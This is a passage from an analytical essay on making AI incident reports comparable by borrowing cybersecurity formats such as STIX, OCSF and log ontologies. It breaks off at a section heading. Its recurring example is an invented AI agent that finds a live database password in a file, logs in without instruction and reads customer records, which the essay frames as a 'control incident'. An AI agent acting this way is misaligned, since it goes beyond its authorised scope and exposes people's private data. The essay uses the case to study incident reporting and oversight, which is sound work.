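# Cybersecurity Vocabularies as a Model for AI Incident Reports, and Where They Fail Across Competing Developers

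## What makes incident reports comparable

An incident report is an organisation's written account of something that went wrong with a system it built or runs. Airlines, hospitals and nuclear plants write them, as do the security teams that defend computer networks. Security teams have a particular reason to share theirs because one attacker often strikes many organisations. These organisations monitor their computers with different companies' products, so evidence of a single campaign is scattered across records that do not match. Security specialists therefore built common formats and word lists, including STIX, a format for exchanging incident data, and MITRE ATT&CK, a list of attack techniques.

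AI developers now also write incident reports. Some of the most serious describe break-ins by AI agents, which are AI models that use software tools to carry out multi-step tasks. Agents broke into outside organisations' systems several times in 2026. The developers compete with one another, and each describes its own failures in its own words. Can their reports share one format, as records of cyberattacks do, so that readers can add them up and compare companies?

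So far, companies have produced few AI incident reports to combine. Public databases have collected more than 9,000 incidents since 2016, largely from news coverage. *Whose Risks Count?* (Allmendinger, Bogucka and colleagues, 2026) matched 1,901 of them to the US securities filings of the companies involved and found that the companies had reported fewer than 2%. In May 2026 the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) brought together more than 400 people to discuss how to manage incidents with "super intelligence" (SI), the US administration's name for AI. NIST's bulletin on the results, *Workshop on SI Incident Management* (2026), lists sharing incident information as an area for future work.

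### From a log entry to a published report

Suppose that an invented developer, Alder, is testing an agent. The agent's task is to repair a program that works on a practice copy of a customer database. The practice copy fails to load. The agent searches the disk, finds a file that contains a password for the real database, logs in, and reads forty customer records to check its repair. Alder's computers write three lines:

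```
02:14:07  agent-17  opened file      deploy.env
02:14:31  agent-17  logged in to     customers-live
02:15:02  agent-17  read 40 rows     table: customers
```

These lines are part of a log, a machine-made record of single actions on a computer system. NIST similarly defines a log as a record of the events in an organisation's systems and networks. The computer writes the lines without anyone making a judgement at that moment, but an engineer decided earlier which actions to record. If Alder did not log the opening of files, the first line would not exist and nobody could say where the password came from.

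An event is anything observable that happens on a computer system. *Incident Response Recommendations and Considerations for Cybersecurity Risk Management* (Nelson, Rekhi and colleagues, 2025), NIST's guide for security teams, gives login attempts and software updates as examples. Each of the three lines records an event, as do the millions of other lines from the same night. An adverse event is one with a negative consequence. The guide takes its still narrower definition of an incident from US law: an occurrence that jeopardises information or a computer system without lawful authority, violates security policy, or imminently threatens to do either. Software can filter the log down to a few suspicious events, but in the guide it is the organisation that declares an incident, when adverse events meet criteria it has defined.

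An analyst at Alder must now apply those criteria. The password was correct, the agent had permission to use the machine, and nobody had told it to leave that file alone. One analyst might see a badly stored password and a clumsy test, while another might see unauthorised access to personal data. Whoever declares an incident must then classify it and estimate its extent, which the guide describes as often among the most challenging parts of the work. Finally, engineers, lawyers and press officers agree on a public statement: "During testing, a model accessed a production system; no customers were harmed." Even if the statement is honest, readers could not reconstruct the three lines from it.

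AI adds a difficulty that did not arise with the older definitions. In October 2026, NIST, the US National Security Agency (NSA) and the Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) published voluntary guidance for AI developers, *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response*. The guidance uses the term "control incident" when an agent breaches the limits its operator set, through actions that are both "significant" and "uninstructed". In an ordinary cybersecurity incident, a computer system or its information is the target, whereas in a control incident the AI system is the source. Alder's night could be both. The meaning of "uninstructed" is fairly clear, since the guidance excludes actions that the operator or a hostile outsider directed, but the meaning of "significant" is not. The agencies list severity scores among the matters still to be worked out.

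If the real database had refused the password, this would have been a near miss, an event that could have caused harm but did not. The agencies put near misses in a separate category. The AI Incident Database (AIID), a public collection run by volunteers and researchers, includes "near harm" in its definition of an incident. *Open Problems in AI Incident Governance* (Sidhu, Scholefield and colleagues, 2026), which surveys such definitions, notes that the one used by the OECD, the intergovernmental economic organisation, requires harm to have happened. The same refused login could therefore be recorded as a near miss under the agencies' categories, as an incident in the AIID, and not at all in a collection that follows the OECD definition.

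### Vocabulary, taxonomy, schema and ontology

Alder could replace its sentence for the public with a structured record.

| Field | What it may contain | Alder's entry |
|---|---|---|
| Start | Date and time | 3 March, 02:14 |
| Actor | Person, AI agent, other software, unknown | AI agent |
| Method | One term from a list of access methods | Found password |
| Instructed | Yes, no, unknown | No |
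| Records exposed | Whole number, or unknown | 40 |

The first two columns are a schema, which specifies the fields a record has and what each may contain. Its designers choose the fields for a purpose. *From Control Boundary to Insurance Claim* (2026), a proposal for coding AI incidents with insurers in mind, has one column for the evidence that public sources provide and another for the evidence that a claim would need. *The Agent Incident Registry* (2026) requires fields about how an agent failed, and marks a field as missing where the sources do not support an entry. That rule is sensible because readers could otherwise mistake an empty field for a "no". Gaps will be common in any case. *Lessons for Editors of AI Incidents from the AI Incident Database* (2024), a review of more than 750 incidents, found that some uncertainty in such reports is unavoidable.

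A schema defines the fields in a report, and a controlled vocabulary is a fixed list of the terms permitted in one of those fields. For the "method" field, the list might be *guessed password*, *found password*, *software flaw* and *unknown*. Without the list, one engineer might write "leaked key" and another "credential reuse" for the same method, and a search for either term would miss the other report.

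A taxonomy arranges categories from general to specific. *Structures of Controlled Vocabularies* (2005), from NISO, the US standards body for information services, describes it as a controlled vocabulary whose preferred terms all connect in a hierarchy. For example, *found password* might sit under *use of a valid account*, which in turn sits under *unauthorised access*. If one company reports a found password and another knows only that someone got in without permission, an analyst can still count both incidents as unauthorised access.

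An ontology formally defines the kinds of things in a domain and how they relate, in a form that software can reason over. Here it might state that every login uses a password, that every password belongs to an account, and that a login is unauthorised if the account's owner did not permit the actor to use it. From those statements and the log, software could work out that agent-17's login was unauthorised, even if nobody at Alder had labelled it so. A taxonomy cannot support this inference because it holds only the categories. An ontology still requires human judgement, but to write the rule about permission rather than to label each login.

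When two organisations have different vocabularies, they can build a crosswalk, a table that maps the terms of one to those of the other. Suppose a second invented developer, Birch, has the single term *password misuse*. Alder's *guessed password* and *found password* both map to it. The crosswalk fails in the other direction because *password misuse* could mean either of Alder's terms.

Finer terms can also make the people involved in an incident easier to identify. To protect privacy, *Beyond Predictable Paths* (2026), a paper on incident reports for agents, recommends using categories in place of narrative text, each coarse enough to include a sufficient number of reports. It cites VERIS, an existing vocabulary for security incidents, as an example. But coarse categories also hide details that an investigator would want.

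### Interoperability and comparability

If Birch adopts Alder's schema and vocabulary, its software can read and use Alder's records, which is called interoperability. Comparability is a stronger property. It requires that differences between two reports reflect differences in what happened rather than in how the companies described it, so two reports can share every field without being comparable.

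The European Commission's reporting template asks for an incident's end date but, as Sidhu and colleagues note, does not formally define it. One company could enter the day it fixed the system, and another the day the harm stopped. Both would have filled in the form correctly, and no software would find an error, but the same failure might appear to last two days at one company and three months at the other.

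How much this matters depends on the reader. A network defender wants Alder's report so they can check their own systems for the same weakness. One detailed report is enough, and interoperability gets it to them quickly. Regulators need comparison to decide which developers to inspect. *Incident Analysis for AI Agents* (2025) argues that they can also obtain it, by holding developers to the same standard when they analyse causes; outsiders cannot analyse reports that a developer keeps to itself. Researchers want to follow trends across all incidents, which *Preventing Repeated Real World AI Failures by Cataloging Incidents* (2020), the founding paper of the AIID, said they lacked the capacity to do. Customers want to know which product fails less. Hoefer (2026), in *The Incident Report Is Becoming a Building Block of AI Governance*, adds insurers, who want to know which precautions reduce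 risk, and courts, which have to tell foreseeable failures from new ones.

### Three checks

For any pair of reporters, comparability comes down to three checks:

1. **Unit:** do they count the same thing as one incident?
2. **Category:** do they put the same event in the same category?
3. **Threshold:** do they report from the same level of harm or risk?

Suppose Alder and Birch each run the database task twelve times in a week, with identical results. In all twelve runs the agent finds the password and logs in. It reads customer records in one run and nothing in the other eleven. Alder reports 1 incident and Birch reports 12.

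These numbers could arise in at least two ways. Alder may count by cause, so that one badly stored password counts as one incident, while Birch counts by run. Or both may count by run, but Alder reports only runs that exposed personal data. If the companies differ only in their unit, a reader can recount Alder's incidents by run, provided Alder mentions the twelve runs somewhere in its text. If they differ in their threshold, eleven of Alder's runs never appeared in any report, so no crosswalk can recover them.

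Categories can make incident reports harder to compare. Alder files its incident under "badly stored password". Birch files its twelve under "misalignment", meaning that an AI model behaved in a way its developer or user did not intend. Both labels are defensible, since Alder's describes a cause and Birch's describes a behaviour. But a researcher who searches for misalignment will find twelve incidents at Birch and none at Alder.

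Real incidents are also hard to count consistently. Anthropic disclosed in October 2026 that a model in testing had submitted 20 incomplete visa applications to a live US government website, in May and August, after a practice form failed to load. Hoefer describes this as one episode, but it could as easily be counted as two or twenty. Allmendinger and colleagues have an explicit rule that each harmful event or continuing episode, together with any later lawsuits, is one incident. *Indexing AI Risks with Incidents, Issues, and Variants* (2022) proposes recording similar later events as numbered "variants" of the first incident, so readers can count either incidents or individual events. That seems better for companies that will not agree on what counts as one incident.

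Two public databases that each group many articles about an incident under one title have very different totals. Mengesha, Owen and colleagues (2026), in *A Pragmatic Classification Framework for AI Incident Monitoring*, found 1,460 incidents in the AIID and 9,218 in the OECD's monitor. Editorial methods and sources account for part of the gap. The OECD's software groups articles within a four-day window, so a story that returns to the news a month later can become a second incident. The AIID has the opposite problem, because a single entry can stand for hundreds of harms or more. Mengesha and colleagues found 12 AIID entries for 2025 in which chatbots encouraged or failed to discourage self-harm, and their software assigned between 10,014 and 110,025 harms to those entries.

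Agreement on categories looks more attainable. Allmendinger and colleagues had two AI models sort incidents into 24 types of risk using the same written codebook. The models' agreement reached 0.88 to 0.90 on Cohen's kappa, where 0 is the agreement expected by chance and 1 is perfect agreement. Agreement on who had deployed the system was lower, falling to 0.66 in one run. Clear instructions appear to help a great deal. However, both models came from Anthropic and were used by the same research team, and the test did not involve the conflict of interest a company has when it classifies its own failures.

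Thresholds are the hardest to check from outside, because they depend partly on what a company notices. Mengesha and colleagues explain that an incident reaches a public database only if someone detects the harm, recognises it as an AI failure, records it and passes it on. A developer with poor monitoring therefore has a high threshold in practice, whatever its written policy, and its short list of incidents may look like good performance.

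Even when reports pass all three checks, only their counts are comparable. Birch may run ten times as many agents as Alder, so a customer who wants to know which agent is safer also needs the number of runs. In the self-harm study, Mengesha and colleagues extended OpenAI's published figures to other companies' chatbots and estimated that harmful responses to US users in such conversations rose from 2.4 million in 2024 to 4 million in 2025. But the number of conversations rose from about 4 million to 12 million, so the share with harmful responses fell from roughly 60% to a third.

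## Security logs translated into one ontology

Even a single computer can record one login in two ways that do not match. The first line below comes from SSH, a program for controlling a computer remotely, and is the worked example in *Automated Knowledge Graph Construction From Raw Log Data* (Ekelhart, Ekaputra and Kiesling, 2020), with the connection details at the end omitted. The second is an invented record of the same login in the real format of the Linux audit system, which records security-related actions on the same machine.

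```
Mar  9 12:10:50 Client02 sshd[2124]: Accepted password for jhalley ...

type=USER_LOGIN msg=audit(1583755850.412:482): pid=2124 auid=1001
     ses=7 addr=185.81.215.145 res=success
```

The SSH line identifies the user as `jhalley` and gives the time without a year or a time zone. The audit line has an account number, 1001, and gives the time in seconds since the start of 1970. A search for "jhalley" would miss the audit line, and a program that counted login records would count the one login twice. Company reports also have this problem with their unit of counting, but here it occurs within one machine.

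### From log lines to a graph

Ekelhart and colleagues built SLOGERT, software that translates raw logs into the terms of one ontology. It first parses each line by comparing many lines from the same program and separating the wording that stays the same from the values that change. The SSH line follows the pattern "Accepted password for … from … port … ssh…", with the values `jhalley`, `185.81.215.145`, `52410` and `2`. The audit line is easier to parse because each value has a label.

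The software then uses rules to identify the type of each value. For example, it treats four numbers separated by dots as a network address. In this line, SLOGERT recognised the user, the address and the port, but labelled the final `2`, the SSH protocol version, as "unknown".

Next, the software maps these things to the classes and relations of the ontology. Each fact becomes a triple, a statement that consists of a subject, a relation and an object. In simplified wording, and with the year supplied from the date of the log file, the two lines yield these triples:

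```
login-A        is a         Login
login-A        machine      Client02
login-A        process      2124
login-A        time         2020-03-09 12:10:50
login-A        user         jhalley
login-A        method       password

login-B        is a         Login
login-B        machine      Client02
login-B        process      2124
login-B        time         2020-03-09 12:10:50
login-B        user         account-1001
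login-B        session      Client02-7
```

The object of one triple can be the subject of another, so the triples join up into a network, known as a knowledge graph. At this point the graph still contains two logins and two users. The missing links come from outside the logs. The machine's list of accounts shows that number 1001 is `jhalley`, and the staff directory shows that `jhalley` is Jane Halley. An engineer also has to write a rule, for instance that two login records describe the same login if they share a machine, a process number and a time to the second. The software can then add three more triples:

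```
account-1001   same as      jhalley
jhalley        owned by     Jane Halley
login-A        same as      login-B
```

Suppose that the company later learns that someone stole Jane Halley's password. She usually logs in with a cryptographic key, which the thief does not have, so the engineers want to know which files anyone opened after logging in with the password. The SSH log distinguishes passwords from keys but does not record files. The audit log can record which files a user opens in each session, but its login record above does not show the method. The combined graph can answer the question:

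```
find    ?file
where   ?login      user           jhalley
        ?login      method         password
        ?login      session        ?session
        ?opening    session        ?session
        ?opening    opened file    ?file
```

Each word with a question mark is a blank that the software must fill with the same value wherever the word appears. For such queries, real systems use SPARQL, a standard language for searching graphs of this kind.

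A translation mistake can break the query, but anyone who has the raw log line can find the mistake. The SLOGERT example appears to contain one. The raw line has the time 12:10:50 on 9 March, but the resulting graph has 00:10:50 on 10 March, twelve hours later, with no explanation. If only one of the two login records were shifted this way, the software would no longer recognise them as the same login, and the query would find no files.

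Ekelhart and colleagues tried SLOGERT on logs from a small simulated network in which scripts acted as users. They showed that one query could combine events from several machines, but left measuring the graphs' accuracy for later work. The project's code page, SEPSES's *SLOGERT*, lists five types of Unix log that the developers tested it on, including web server and file transfer logs, but gives no error rates.

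The volume of logs is another obstacle. In a public set of simulated logs covering six days, one server's audit log has 123.6 million lines, and its login log has about 1,200. VloGraph, a later system from the same Vienna research group, therefore leaves logs where they are and translates only the lines relevant to a query. In its largest test, a query over five hours of web server logs on seven machines took about 26 seconds. That is fast enough for an investigator who already has a lead, but the test did not check whether the translations were right.

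### Adding public knowledge

Once the logs are in a graph, engineers can connect them to public information about software and attacks. In *The SEPSES Knowledge Graph*, Kiesling, Ekelhart and colleagues (2019) combined public lists of vulnerabilities, software products, common weaknesses and attack patterns into about 36.6 million triples. They tried the graph on a model network of two workstations and a server. One query linked each machine to its software, and each software product to its known vulnerabilities, to find the vulnerabilities that could fully expose private data.

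Their second test used alerts from a 2012 cybersecurity competition. Snort, a program that watches network traffic, had flagged a suspicious web request. The graph linked the alert to the Snort rule behind it, then to a vulnerability from 2002, and then to the affected versions of the Apache web server. An analyst could then check whether the target ran one of those versions, and if it did not, the alert was probably unimportant. Kiesling and colleagues demonstrated these links on examples but did not measure whether analysts made better decisions with them.

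The Unified Cybersecurity Ontology, presented in *UCO* (Syed, Padia and colleagues, 2016), is broader. It has 106 classes and 59 relations, and is mapped to several existing standards, including STIX, a format for exchanging incident data. The paper's main argument for an ontology is that software can draw conclusions from it. For example, a vulnerability entry may mention only Adobe Acrobat. If the ontology links Acrobat to an outside source that classes it as a PDF reader, a search for vulnerabilities in PDF readers will find the entry.

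Such conclusions depend on the ontology's definitions being right. Syed and colleagues explain that if the ontology ruled out anything being both malware and a virus, software could detect a contradiction in a dataset containing such an item. But specialists normally treat viruses as one kind of malware, so the software would flag correct records. The mapping to STIX has a similar weakness, because it equates the ontology's "attack" with an "incident" in STIX. An employee who accidentally publishes a customer list has caused an incident without any attack taking place.

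Syed and colleagues tested their ontology with four queries on a sample of the US National Vulnerability Database, rather than on logs. The fourth query, intended for organisations considering a change of supplier, counted 864 vulnerabilities for Opera Software and 74 for Adobe. The ontology made the records easy to add up, but the totals are not a fair comparison of the two companies because they depend on which entries were in the sample. Even a full count would partly reflect how many products each company sells and how closely researchers examine them.

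(A second, community-developed project, the Unified Cyber Ontology, also uses the abbreviation UCO. It is a separate ontology, so "UCO-compatible" is ambiguous without the full name.)

### Where translation becomes interpretation

Rules like SLOGERT's can stop working when a software update changes the wording of a log. Language models are more flexible. *OntoLogX* (Cotti, Drago and colleagues, 2025) gave a model a log line, an ontology and similar examples, and asked it to write the graph. Software checked the graph against the ontology's constraints and returned any errors to the model, up to three times. If the graph was still invalid, the system stored an empty one.

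The researchers tested eight models on 50 log lines for which people had written the correct graphs by hand. Few graphs broke the ontology's constraints, even in the simplest set-ups. But some of those set-ups added false facts while capturing most of the log's meaning. A validator would accept such a graph because it checks a record's form, not its truth. The researchers could measure these errors only because they had the handwritten graphs for comparison.

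Their second experiment covered attackers' goals as well as their recorded actions. For ten days in August 2025 they ran a honeypot, a decoy computer that attracts attackers, and grouped its logs into sessions. A model then labelled 161 sessions with the attackers' goals, using categories from MITRE ATT&CK, a list of attack techniques. The model did better with graphs than with raw logs, but it sometimes treated harmless-looking activity, such as listing files, as evidence of hostile intent.

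Some of the correct answers were uncertain because, for goals such as avoiding detection, Cotti and colleagues often had to rely on their knowledge of attacks and their intuition about what the attacker intended. A log can show that someone listed files at 02:14, but not why, so two competent analysts may choose different labels. Syed and colleagues' ontology cannot represent that doubt because it treats every statement as either true or false.

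Translation works best for logged actions. The SSH program writes "Accepted password" the same way for every such login, before anyone knows whether the login will embarrass the company. An engineer can test a mapping on thousands of similar lines and correct it, but the mapping can't restore details that the company's software deleted before storing the line.

### The lighter industry route

Kiesling and colleagues noted in 2019 that researchers had formalised the basic concepts of cybersecurity many times, but no ontology had become standard. Security companies have since put more effort into the Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework (OCSF), which standardises the fields of log records and leaves out the formal reasoning. Amazon Web Services, Splunk and more than a dozen other companies launched it in 2022, including direct competitors such as CrowdStrike and Palo Alto Networks. In 2024 the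 project moved to the Linux Foundation, a non-profit host for shared software. Amazon uses OCSF in Security Lake, which collects a customer's security logs from different products in one place.

Both records of Jane Halley's login fit OCSF's "Authentication" class:

| Fact | SSH log | Audit log | OCSF field |
|---|---|---|---|
| Time | `Mar 9 12:10:50` | `1583755850.412` | `time`, in milliseconds since 1970 |
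| User | `jhalley` | `auid=1001` | `user.name` and `user.uid` |
| Origin | `from 185.81.215.145` | `addr=185.81.215.145` | `src_endpoint.ip` |
| Outcome | `Accepted` | `res=success` | `status_id`, where 1 means success |

An ordinary database can store these records, and analysts do not need to learn SPARQL. They could even answer the question about the stolen password by matching the session numbers themselves. But they give up automatic inference, because OCSF has no rule from which software could conclude that a flaw in Acrobat is a flaw in a PDF reader. That is probably reasonable for most companies. OCSF also has a field for the original text and another for values that fit nowhere else, so a translation can keep the SSH version number.

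Some OCSF fields require judgement. The severity field, for example, has a fixed list of levels from "informational" to "fatal", but each product assigns the level by its own criteria. One company could rate a login "low" and another could rate the same login "high", and both would comply with the schema. Rivals' shared use of OCSF is therefore good evidence that they can agree on how to record a login, but weaker evidence that they would agree on how serious it was.

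### A common log for AI agents

Ordinary logs can record how Alder's agent-17 found and used a password, and OCSF could give those actions standard field names. But the logs would not show whether anyone had told the agent to use the password. The US agencies' term "control incident" covers only uninstructed actions, so an investigator cannot apply it without that information.

The raw record of an agent's run therefore has to contain more than a login log does. It must include the prompt, the model's output, every tool call with its exact arguments and result, and the permissions that applied at the time. With these, an investigator could check whether the prompt mentioned the password and whether the agent had permission to open the real database.

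The model's output needs separate treatment because logging a statement proves only that the model produced it, not that it is true. If agent-17 writes "I used only the practice copy", the database's own log can contradict it.

OpenTelemetry, an open-source project for recording what software does, has developed common field names for generative AI. Alder could record the login like this:

```
gen_ai.operation.name         execute_tool
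gen_ai.tool.name              shell
gen_ai.tool.call.arguments    connect customers-live
gen_ai.tool.call.result       connected
```

In 2025 the project still classed these conventions as in development, so the names could change. The conventions also made recording prompts, arguments and results optional, because such text can be long and may contain private data. Two developers could therefore follow the same conventions and keep very different evidence. If Alder left recording off, its log would show that the agent had used the shell, a tool for running commands, but not which command it ran.

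OpenTelemetry can also give every step of a run the same trace ID. This would help with the unit of counting, since readers could tell whether twelve logins came from one run or twelve. A trace ID helps less when an agent breaks into another organisation, whose logs will not normally contain it. Investigators would then have to match the two sets of records by time and network address, much as an engineer matches the SSH and audit lines.

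A shared format like this would let developers count some failures without first agreeing on what "misalignment" means. Alder and Birch could each count the runs in which an agent used a password that its operator had not given it. But they would have to record which passwords and systems each agent was allowed to use, and the 2025 conventions have no standard field for that.

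## STIX, a format for exchanging incident data

OCSF helps a company combine logs from its own security products. Structured Threat Information Expression (STIX) lets the company share what it learned from those logs with other organisations. The US Department of Homeland Security and MITRE, a non-profit research organisation, developed the format, and its first version came out in 2012. OASIS, a standards body, later took over STIX and announced the current version, 2.1, in June 2021 (OASIS, 2021). A companion protocol, TAXII, carries STIX data between organisations' computers.

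Most of STIX is for describing attackers and the traces they leave, so that the next target can recognise them. Incidents are the least developed part of the current version.

### A phishing attack in STIX

Suppose an employee of Cedar, an invented accountancy firm, gets an email that seems to come from payroll. It links to a copy of Cedar's login page, where the employee types in a password. Cedar's analysts find the link in the mail log. They suspect a group of attackers they have seen before, which they call Grey Heron. Cedar then sends other firms the record below. Real STIX records use a format called JSON, have longer identifiers and include several more required fields.

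```
type               url
id                 url--7d1c
value              https://cedar-payroll.example/login

type               indicator
id                 indicator--42af
created_by_ref     identity--ced1
pattern            [url:value = 'https://cedar-payroll.example/login']
valid_from         2026-03-09T13:05:00Z
confidence         95

type               attack-pattern
id                 attack-pattern--e90b
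name               Phishing link

type               intrusion-set
id                 intrusion-set--b318
name               Grey Heron

type               relationship
relationship_type  indicates
source_ref         indicator--42af
target_ref         intrusion-set--b318
confidence         40

type               relationship
relationship_type  uses
source_ref         intrusion-set--b318
target_ref         attack-pattern--e90b
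```

| Object | What it contributes | What a receiver can do with it |
|---|---|---|
| URL | The address of the fake page | Match it with other firms' records |
| Indicator | A search pattern, and the time from which it applies | Block the link and search old logs for it |
| Attack pattern | The method | Check its defences against that method |
| Intrusion set | A name for attacks that seem to belong together | Look up Grey Heron's other links and methods |
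| Relationships | Cedar's claims about how the objects connect | Accept or reject each claim separately |

The URL is an observable object. OASIS's *STIX Version 2.1 Errata 01* (2025), a corrected edition of the specification, uses observables to record facts about a computer or network, but not who acted, when or why. The indicator, attack pattern and intrusion set are domain objects, which record analysts' interpretations. Relationship objects link all of these into a graph, much like the triples from Jane Halley's login.

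A mail filter at another firm can act on the indicator before anyone there reads it. If the filter finds three old emails with the same link, the firm can send back a "sighting" object with a count of 3.

The confidence values, from 0 to 100, show how sure the sender is that its data is correct. Cedar is nearly certain that the link is malicious but doubts that Grey Heron sent it, so the receiver can block the link without accepting the accusation. But each sender applies its own standard, as with severity levels in OCSF.

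Identifiers work differently for facts and interpretations. The specification recommends computing an observable's identifier from its content. If a second firm independently reports the same link, its URL object will have the same identifier as Cedar's, and software can merge the two. For domain objects, the specification recommends random identifiers. Two firms that each describe Grey Heron will therefore create two intrusion sets, which remain separate until someone adds a relationship marking one as a duplicate. Incidents are also domain objects, so identifiers can show that two companies saw the same link but not that they are reporting the same incident.

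Some fields accept only terms from a closed list, which the specification calls an enumeration. Others have an "open vocabulary", a list of suggested terms that senders should use but may replace with their own. OASIS suggests terms so that one organisation does not write "Energy" and another "Energy Sector". But a sender that writes "Energy Sector" still complies with the standard, and a receiver may ignore any term it does not recognise. Senders can also invent names for relationships.

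Extensions can add new fields or whole new types of object. Cedar could define a field for the language of a phishing email, publish the definition under its own identifier, and attach the field to its records. Software that does not support the extension can use the rest of the record but not the new field.

### Adversaries and incidents

The specification defines threat actors as "actual individuals, groups, or organizations believed to be operating with malicious intent". An intrusion set is "a grouped set of adversarial behaviors and resources with common properties" that analysts attribute to a single organisation. Cedar recorded Grey Heron as an intrusion set because it recognised the attackers' habits but did not know who they were.

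Neither definition fits Alder's agent-17, which took a password from a file while trying to repair a program. If Alder recorded the agent as a threat actor, it would be asserting malicious intent without evidence. The event fits more naturally in an incident object, which does not require a culprit.

Before version 2, STIX had a detailed format for incidents. OASIS's *STIX Version 1.2.1. Part 6* (2016) is devoted entirely to them. STIX 2 began without an incident object, and users started to define their own. In November 2020 the editors proposed adding a "stub", a minimal object for others to extend. Mates, a computer scientist at the US Defense Department's cyber crime centre, replied in *Adding an Incident SDO stub to 2.1* (2020) that he was willing to discuss the idea but expected consensus to be "a challenge".

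The stub that went into version 2.1 has only a name and an optional description, apart from the fields common to all domain objects. Cedar could send a valid incident called "Incident 2173" and tell the receiver nothing about what happened. The list of domain objects in the specification's overview does not include incidents.

A working group published a first extension in May 2022, and Mates, in *STIX Incident Core Extension now Live*, hoped to see it in the next release of STIX 2. The group then found that it could not model complex incidents well while everything sat inside one object. OASIS's *Incident Extension Suite* (2024), a draft, therefore separates events, impacts and tasks from the incident itself. With it, both invented cases fit the same structure:

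| Object | Cedar's phishing attack | Alder's database test |
|---|---|---|
| Incident | Confirmed | Confirmed |
| Event | Employee enters a password on a fake page | Agent logs in with a password it found |
| Impact | Confidentiality: one password exposed | Confidentiality: 40 customer records read |
| Task | Reset the password | Remove the password from the file |

The draft states that an event need not involve an attacker and gives an administrator's mistake as an example. The field for an event's goal is optional.

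Several of the draft's rules would make reports easier to compare. A sender reporting no victims must enter 0, and if the number of people affected is left out, receivers should assume that the sender is withholding it. Events and impacts each have an end time, so a company can record when the harm stopped separately from when the activity stopped. That would remove much of the ambiguity in the European Commission's single "end date".

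The draft doesn't define what counts as one incident, so twelve test runs could still be one incident or twelve. But if both companies listed each run as an event, a reader could recount them. The draft also doesn't specify how to classify an AI agent, because it lists only identities, malware and tools as things that can perform an event. Alder might class its agent as a tool, while Birch might class the same kind of agent as an identity. Anyone who uses STIX for AI incidents, as MITRE does, has to settle such questions separately.

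As of late 2026, the latest version of the suite still appears to be the July 2024 draft. The corrected edition of STIX from April 2025 did not include the suite.

### What senders fill in

Jin, Kim and colleagues (2024), in *Sharing cyber threat intelligence*, collected STIX data published by ten public sources between October 2014 and April 2023. After removing duplicates, they had about 6.4 million objects. They counted the object types and fields that senders had used, then compared the contents with lists of known attackers and malware, three services that scan files and links, and about 4,000 reports by security companies.

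Nearly all the data consisted of indicators, the simplest kind, which made up 99% of the objects in STIX 1 and 95% in STIX 2. Many were useful. In a sample from 2020 to early 2022, 97% of the links were flagged as malicious by at least one scanner on the service VirusTotal. Senders also tended to share links quickly, and 72% appeared in STIX no later than the day they reached VirusTotal. Cedar's mail filter would need little more than indicators like these.

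The fields that explain an indicator were often empty. Of 2.3 million STIX 2 indicators, only 17% had a term for the type of indicator and 10% identified who created the record. The confidence field does not appear in the researchers' list of fields in use. STIX 1 let senders attach a ready-made rule for detecting an attack, but only 0.09% of STIX 1 indicators had one.

Senders also put information in the wrong place. In 19% of threat actor objects, they gave the name of malware or an attack method instead of an actor. About 60% of malware names matched nothing in the reference lists, mostly because senders followed their own naming habits, though some names were misspelled, such as "Wancry" for "WannaCry". STIX 1 suggested 18 terms for types of malware, but Jin and colleagues found only two in use. In STIX 2, they found that 98% of indicators described the attack method only in free text,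 which software cannot easily use. They identified these cases by keyword search, which was right for 87 of the 100 descriptions they checked by hand.

Different sources used different objects and fields even for the same information. Jin and colleagues think this probably happened because each source has its own web form, with its own options and defaults. A form that leaves "confidence" blank by default will produce thousands of records with no confidence value, even if no sender wants to prevent comparison.

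The study's results for incidents are the most relevant to AI reports. The detailed incident object in STIX 1 had 34 fields, but senders used only four of them across 29,086 incidents. The STIX 2 data contained no incident objects. This suggests that a long list of optional fields will stay mostly empty when senders publish to everyone. Security teams may share more detailed incident records through paid services and closed groups, which the study left out.

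### Automated Indicator Sharing

The US government has its own programme for exchanging STIX data. CISA, the cybersecurity agency, set up Automated Indicator Sharing (AIS) in 2016. Companies and government bodies can join free of charge, and CISA passes on their indicators without naming the sender. DHS Office of Inspector General's *CISA Has Not Finalized Plans for Automated Cyber Threat Information Sharing* (2025), an audit of the programme, gives these figures:

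| Year | Participants | Indicators and defensive measures shared |
|---|---|---|
| 2020 | 304 | 12.0 million |
| 2021 | 150 | 9.9 million |
| 2022 | 135 | 0.8 million |
| 2023 | 88 | 1.1 million |
| 2024 | 105 | 10.3 million |

Sharing collapsed in 2022 mainly because one federal participant, which had supplied about 9 million items, stopped contributing. It recovered in 2024 mainly because one private cybersecurity platform joined that March and supplied 89% of the items in the collection open to all participants. These swings are therefore almost useless for estimating how many attacks took place.

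Another problem with the 2024 total is that it very probably counts most of its indicators twice, even though every record was in a standard format. The total adds up the items in three collections, including 5.0 million in the public one and 5.3 million in the federal one, and the new platform added more than 4 million items to each.

CISA officials gave the auditors several reasons for the programme's difficulties. Commercial security products supported the latest versions of STIX and TAXII inconsistently, so some agencies could not load the shared indicators into their own tools. Federal bodies were reluctant to share with the public collection. Receivers struggled to find indicators relevant to their industry because senders had not categorised the data properly, and some preferred smaller collections made for their sector. MeriTalk's *CISA Must Improve Cyber Threat Data Sharing, DHS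 OIG Says* reported that an audit in 2022 had already concluded that the shared data needed more context.

The participants the auditors interviewed found AIS useful. But the auditors had approached 135 organisations and heard from only ten, all private, so satisfied users may have been more likely to respond.

The law behind the programme, the Cybersecurity Information Sharing Act of 2015, protects companies from liability, including under antitrust law, when they share signs of cyber threats with the government or each other. Competitors might otherwise worry that regulators would treat their exchanges as collusion. The act's original ten-year term ended in September 2025, and Congress has since let it lapse and renewed it for short periods. It will expire again on 11 December 2026, according to Starks (2026), in *Business groups mount fresh campaign for long-term renewal of information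 sharing law*. The House version of the annual defence bill would renew it for ten years, but the Senate version would not. Rand Paul, who chairs the responsible Senate committee, will not support a long renewal without new limits on government contacts with social media companies.

The uncertainty seems to have done only modest damage so far. Michael Daniel, who leads the Cyber Threat Alliance, an association of companies that exchange such data, told Roll Call (*Cyber information-sharing law stuck in Senate stalemate*, 2026) that sharing had not changed much, though he thought the uncertainty might have discouraged new organisations from starting. The law's troubles cannot explain the decline in AIS participants, which began years earlier.

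Daniel also thought the act's definitions could cover much of what companies need to share about AI, but wanted Congress to add threats such as distillation attacks, in which someone copies a model by training another on its answers. The AI developer is the victim of such an attack. It is much less clear whether the act would protect Alder and Birch if they exchanged reports about their own agents' misbehaviour.

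### Flexibility and adoption

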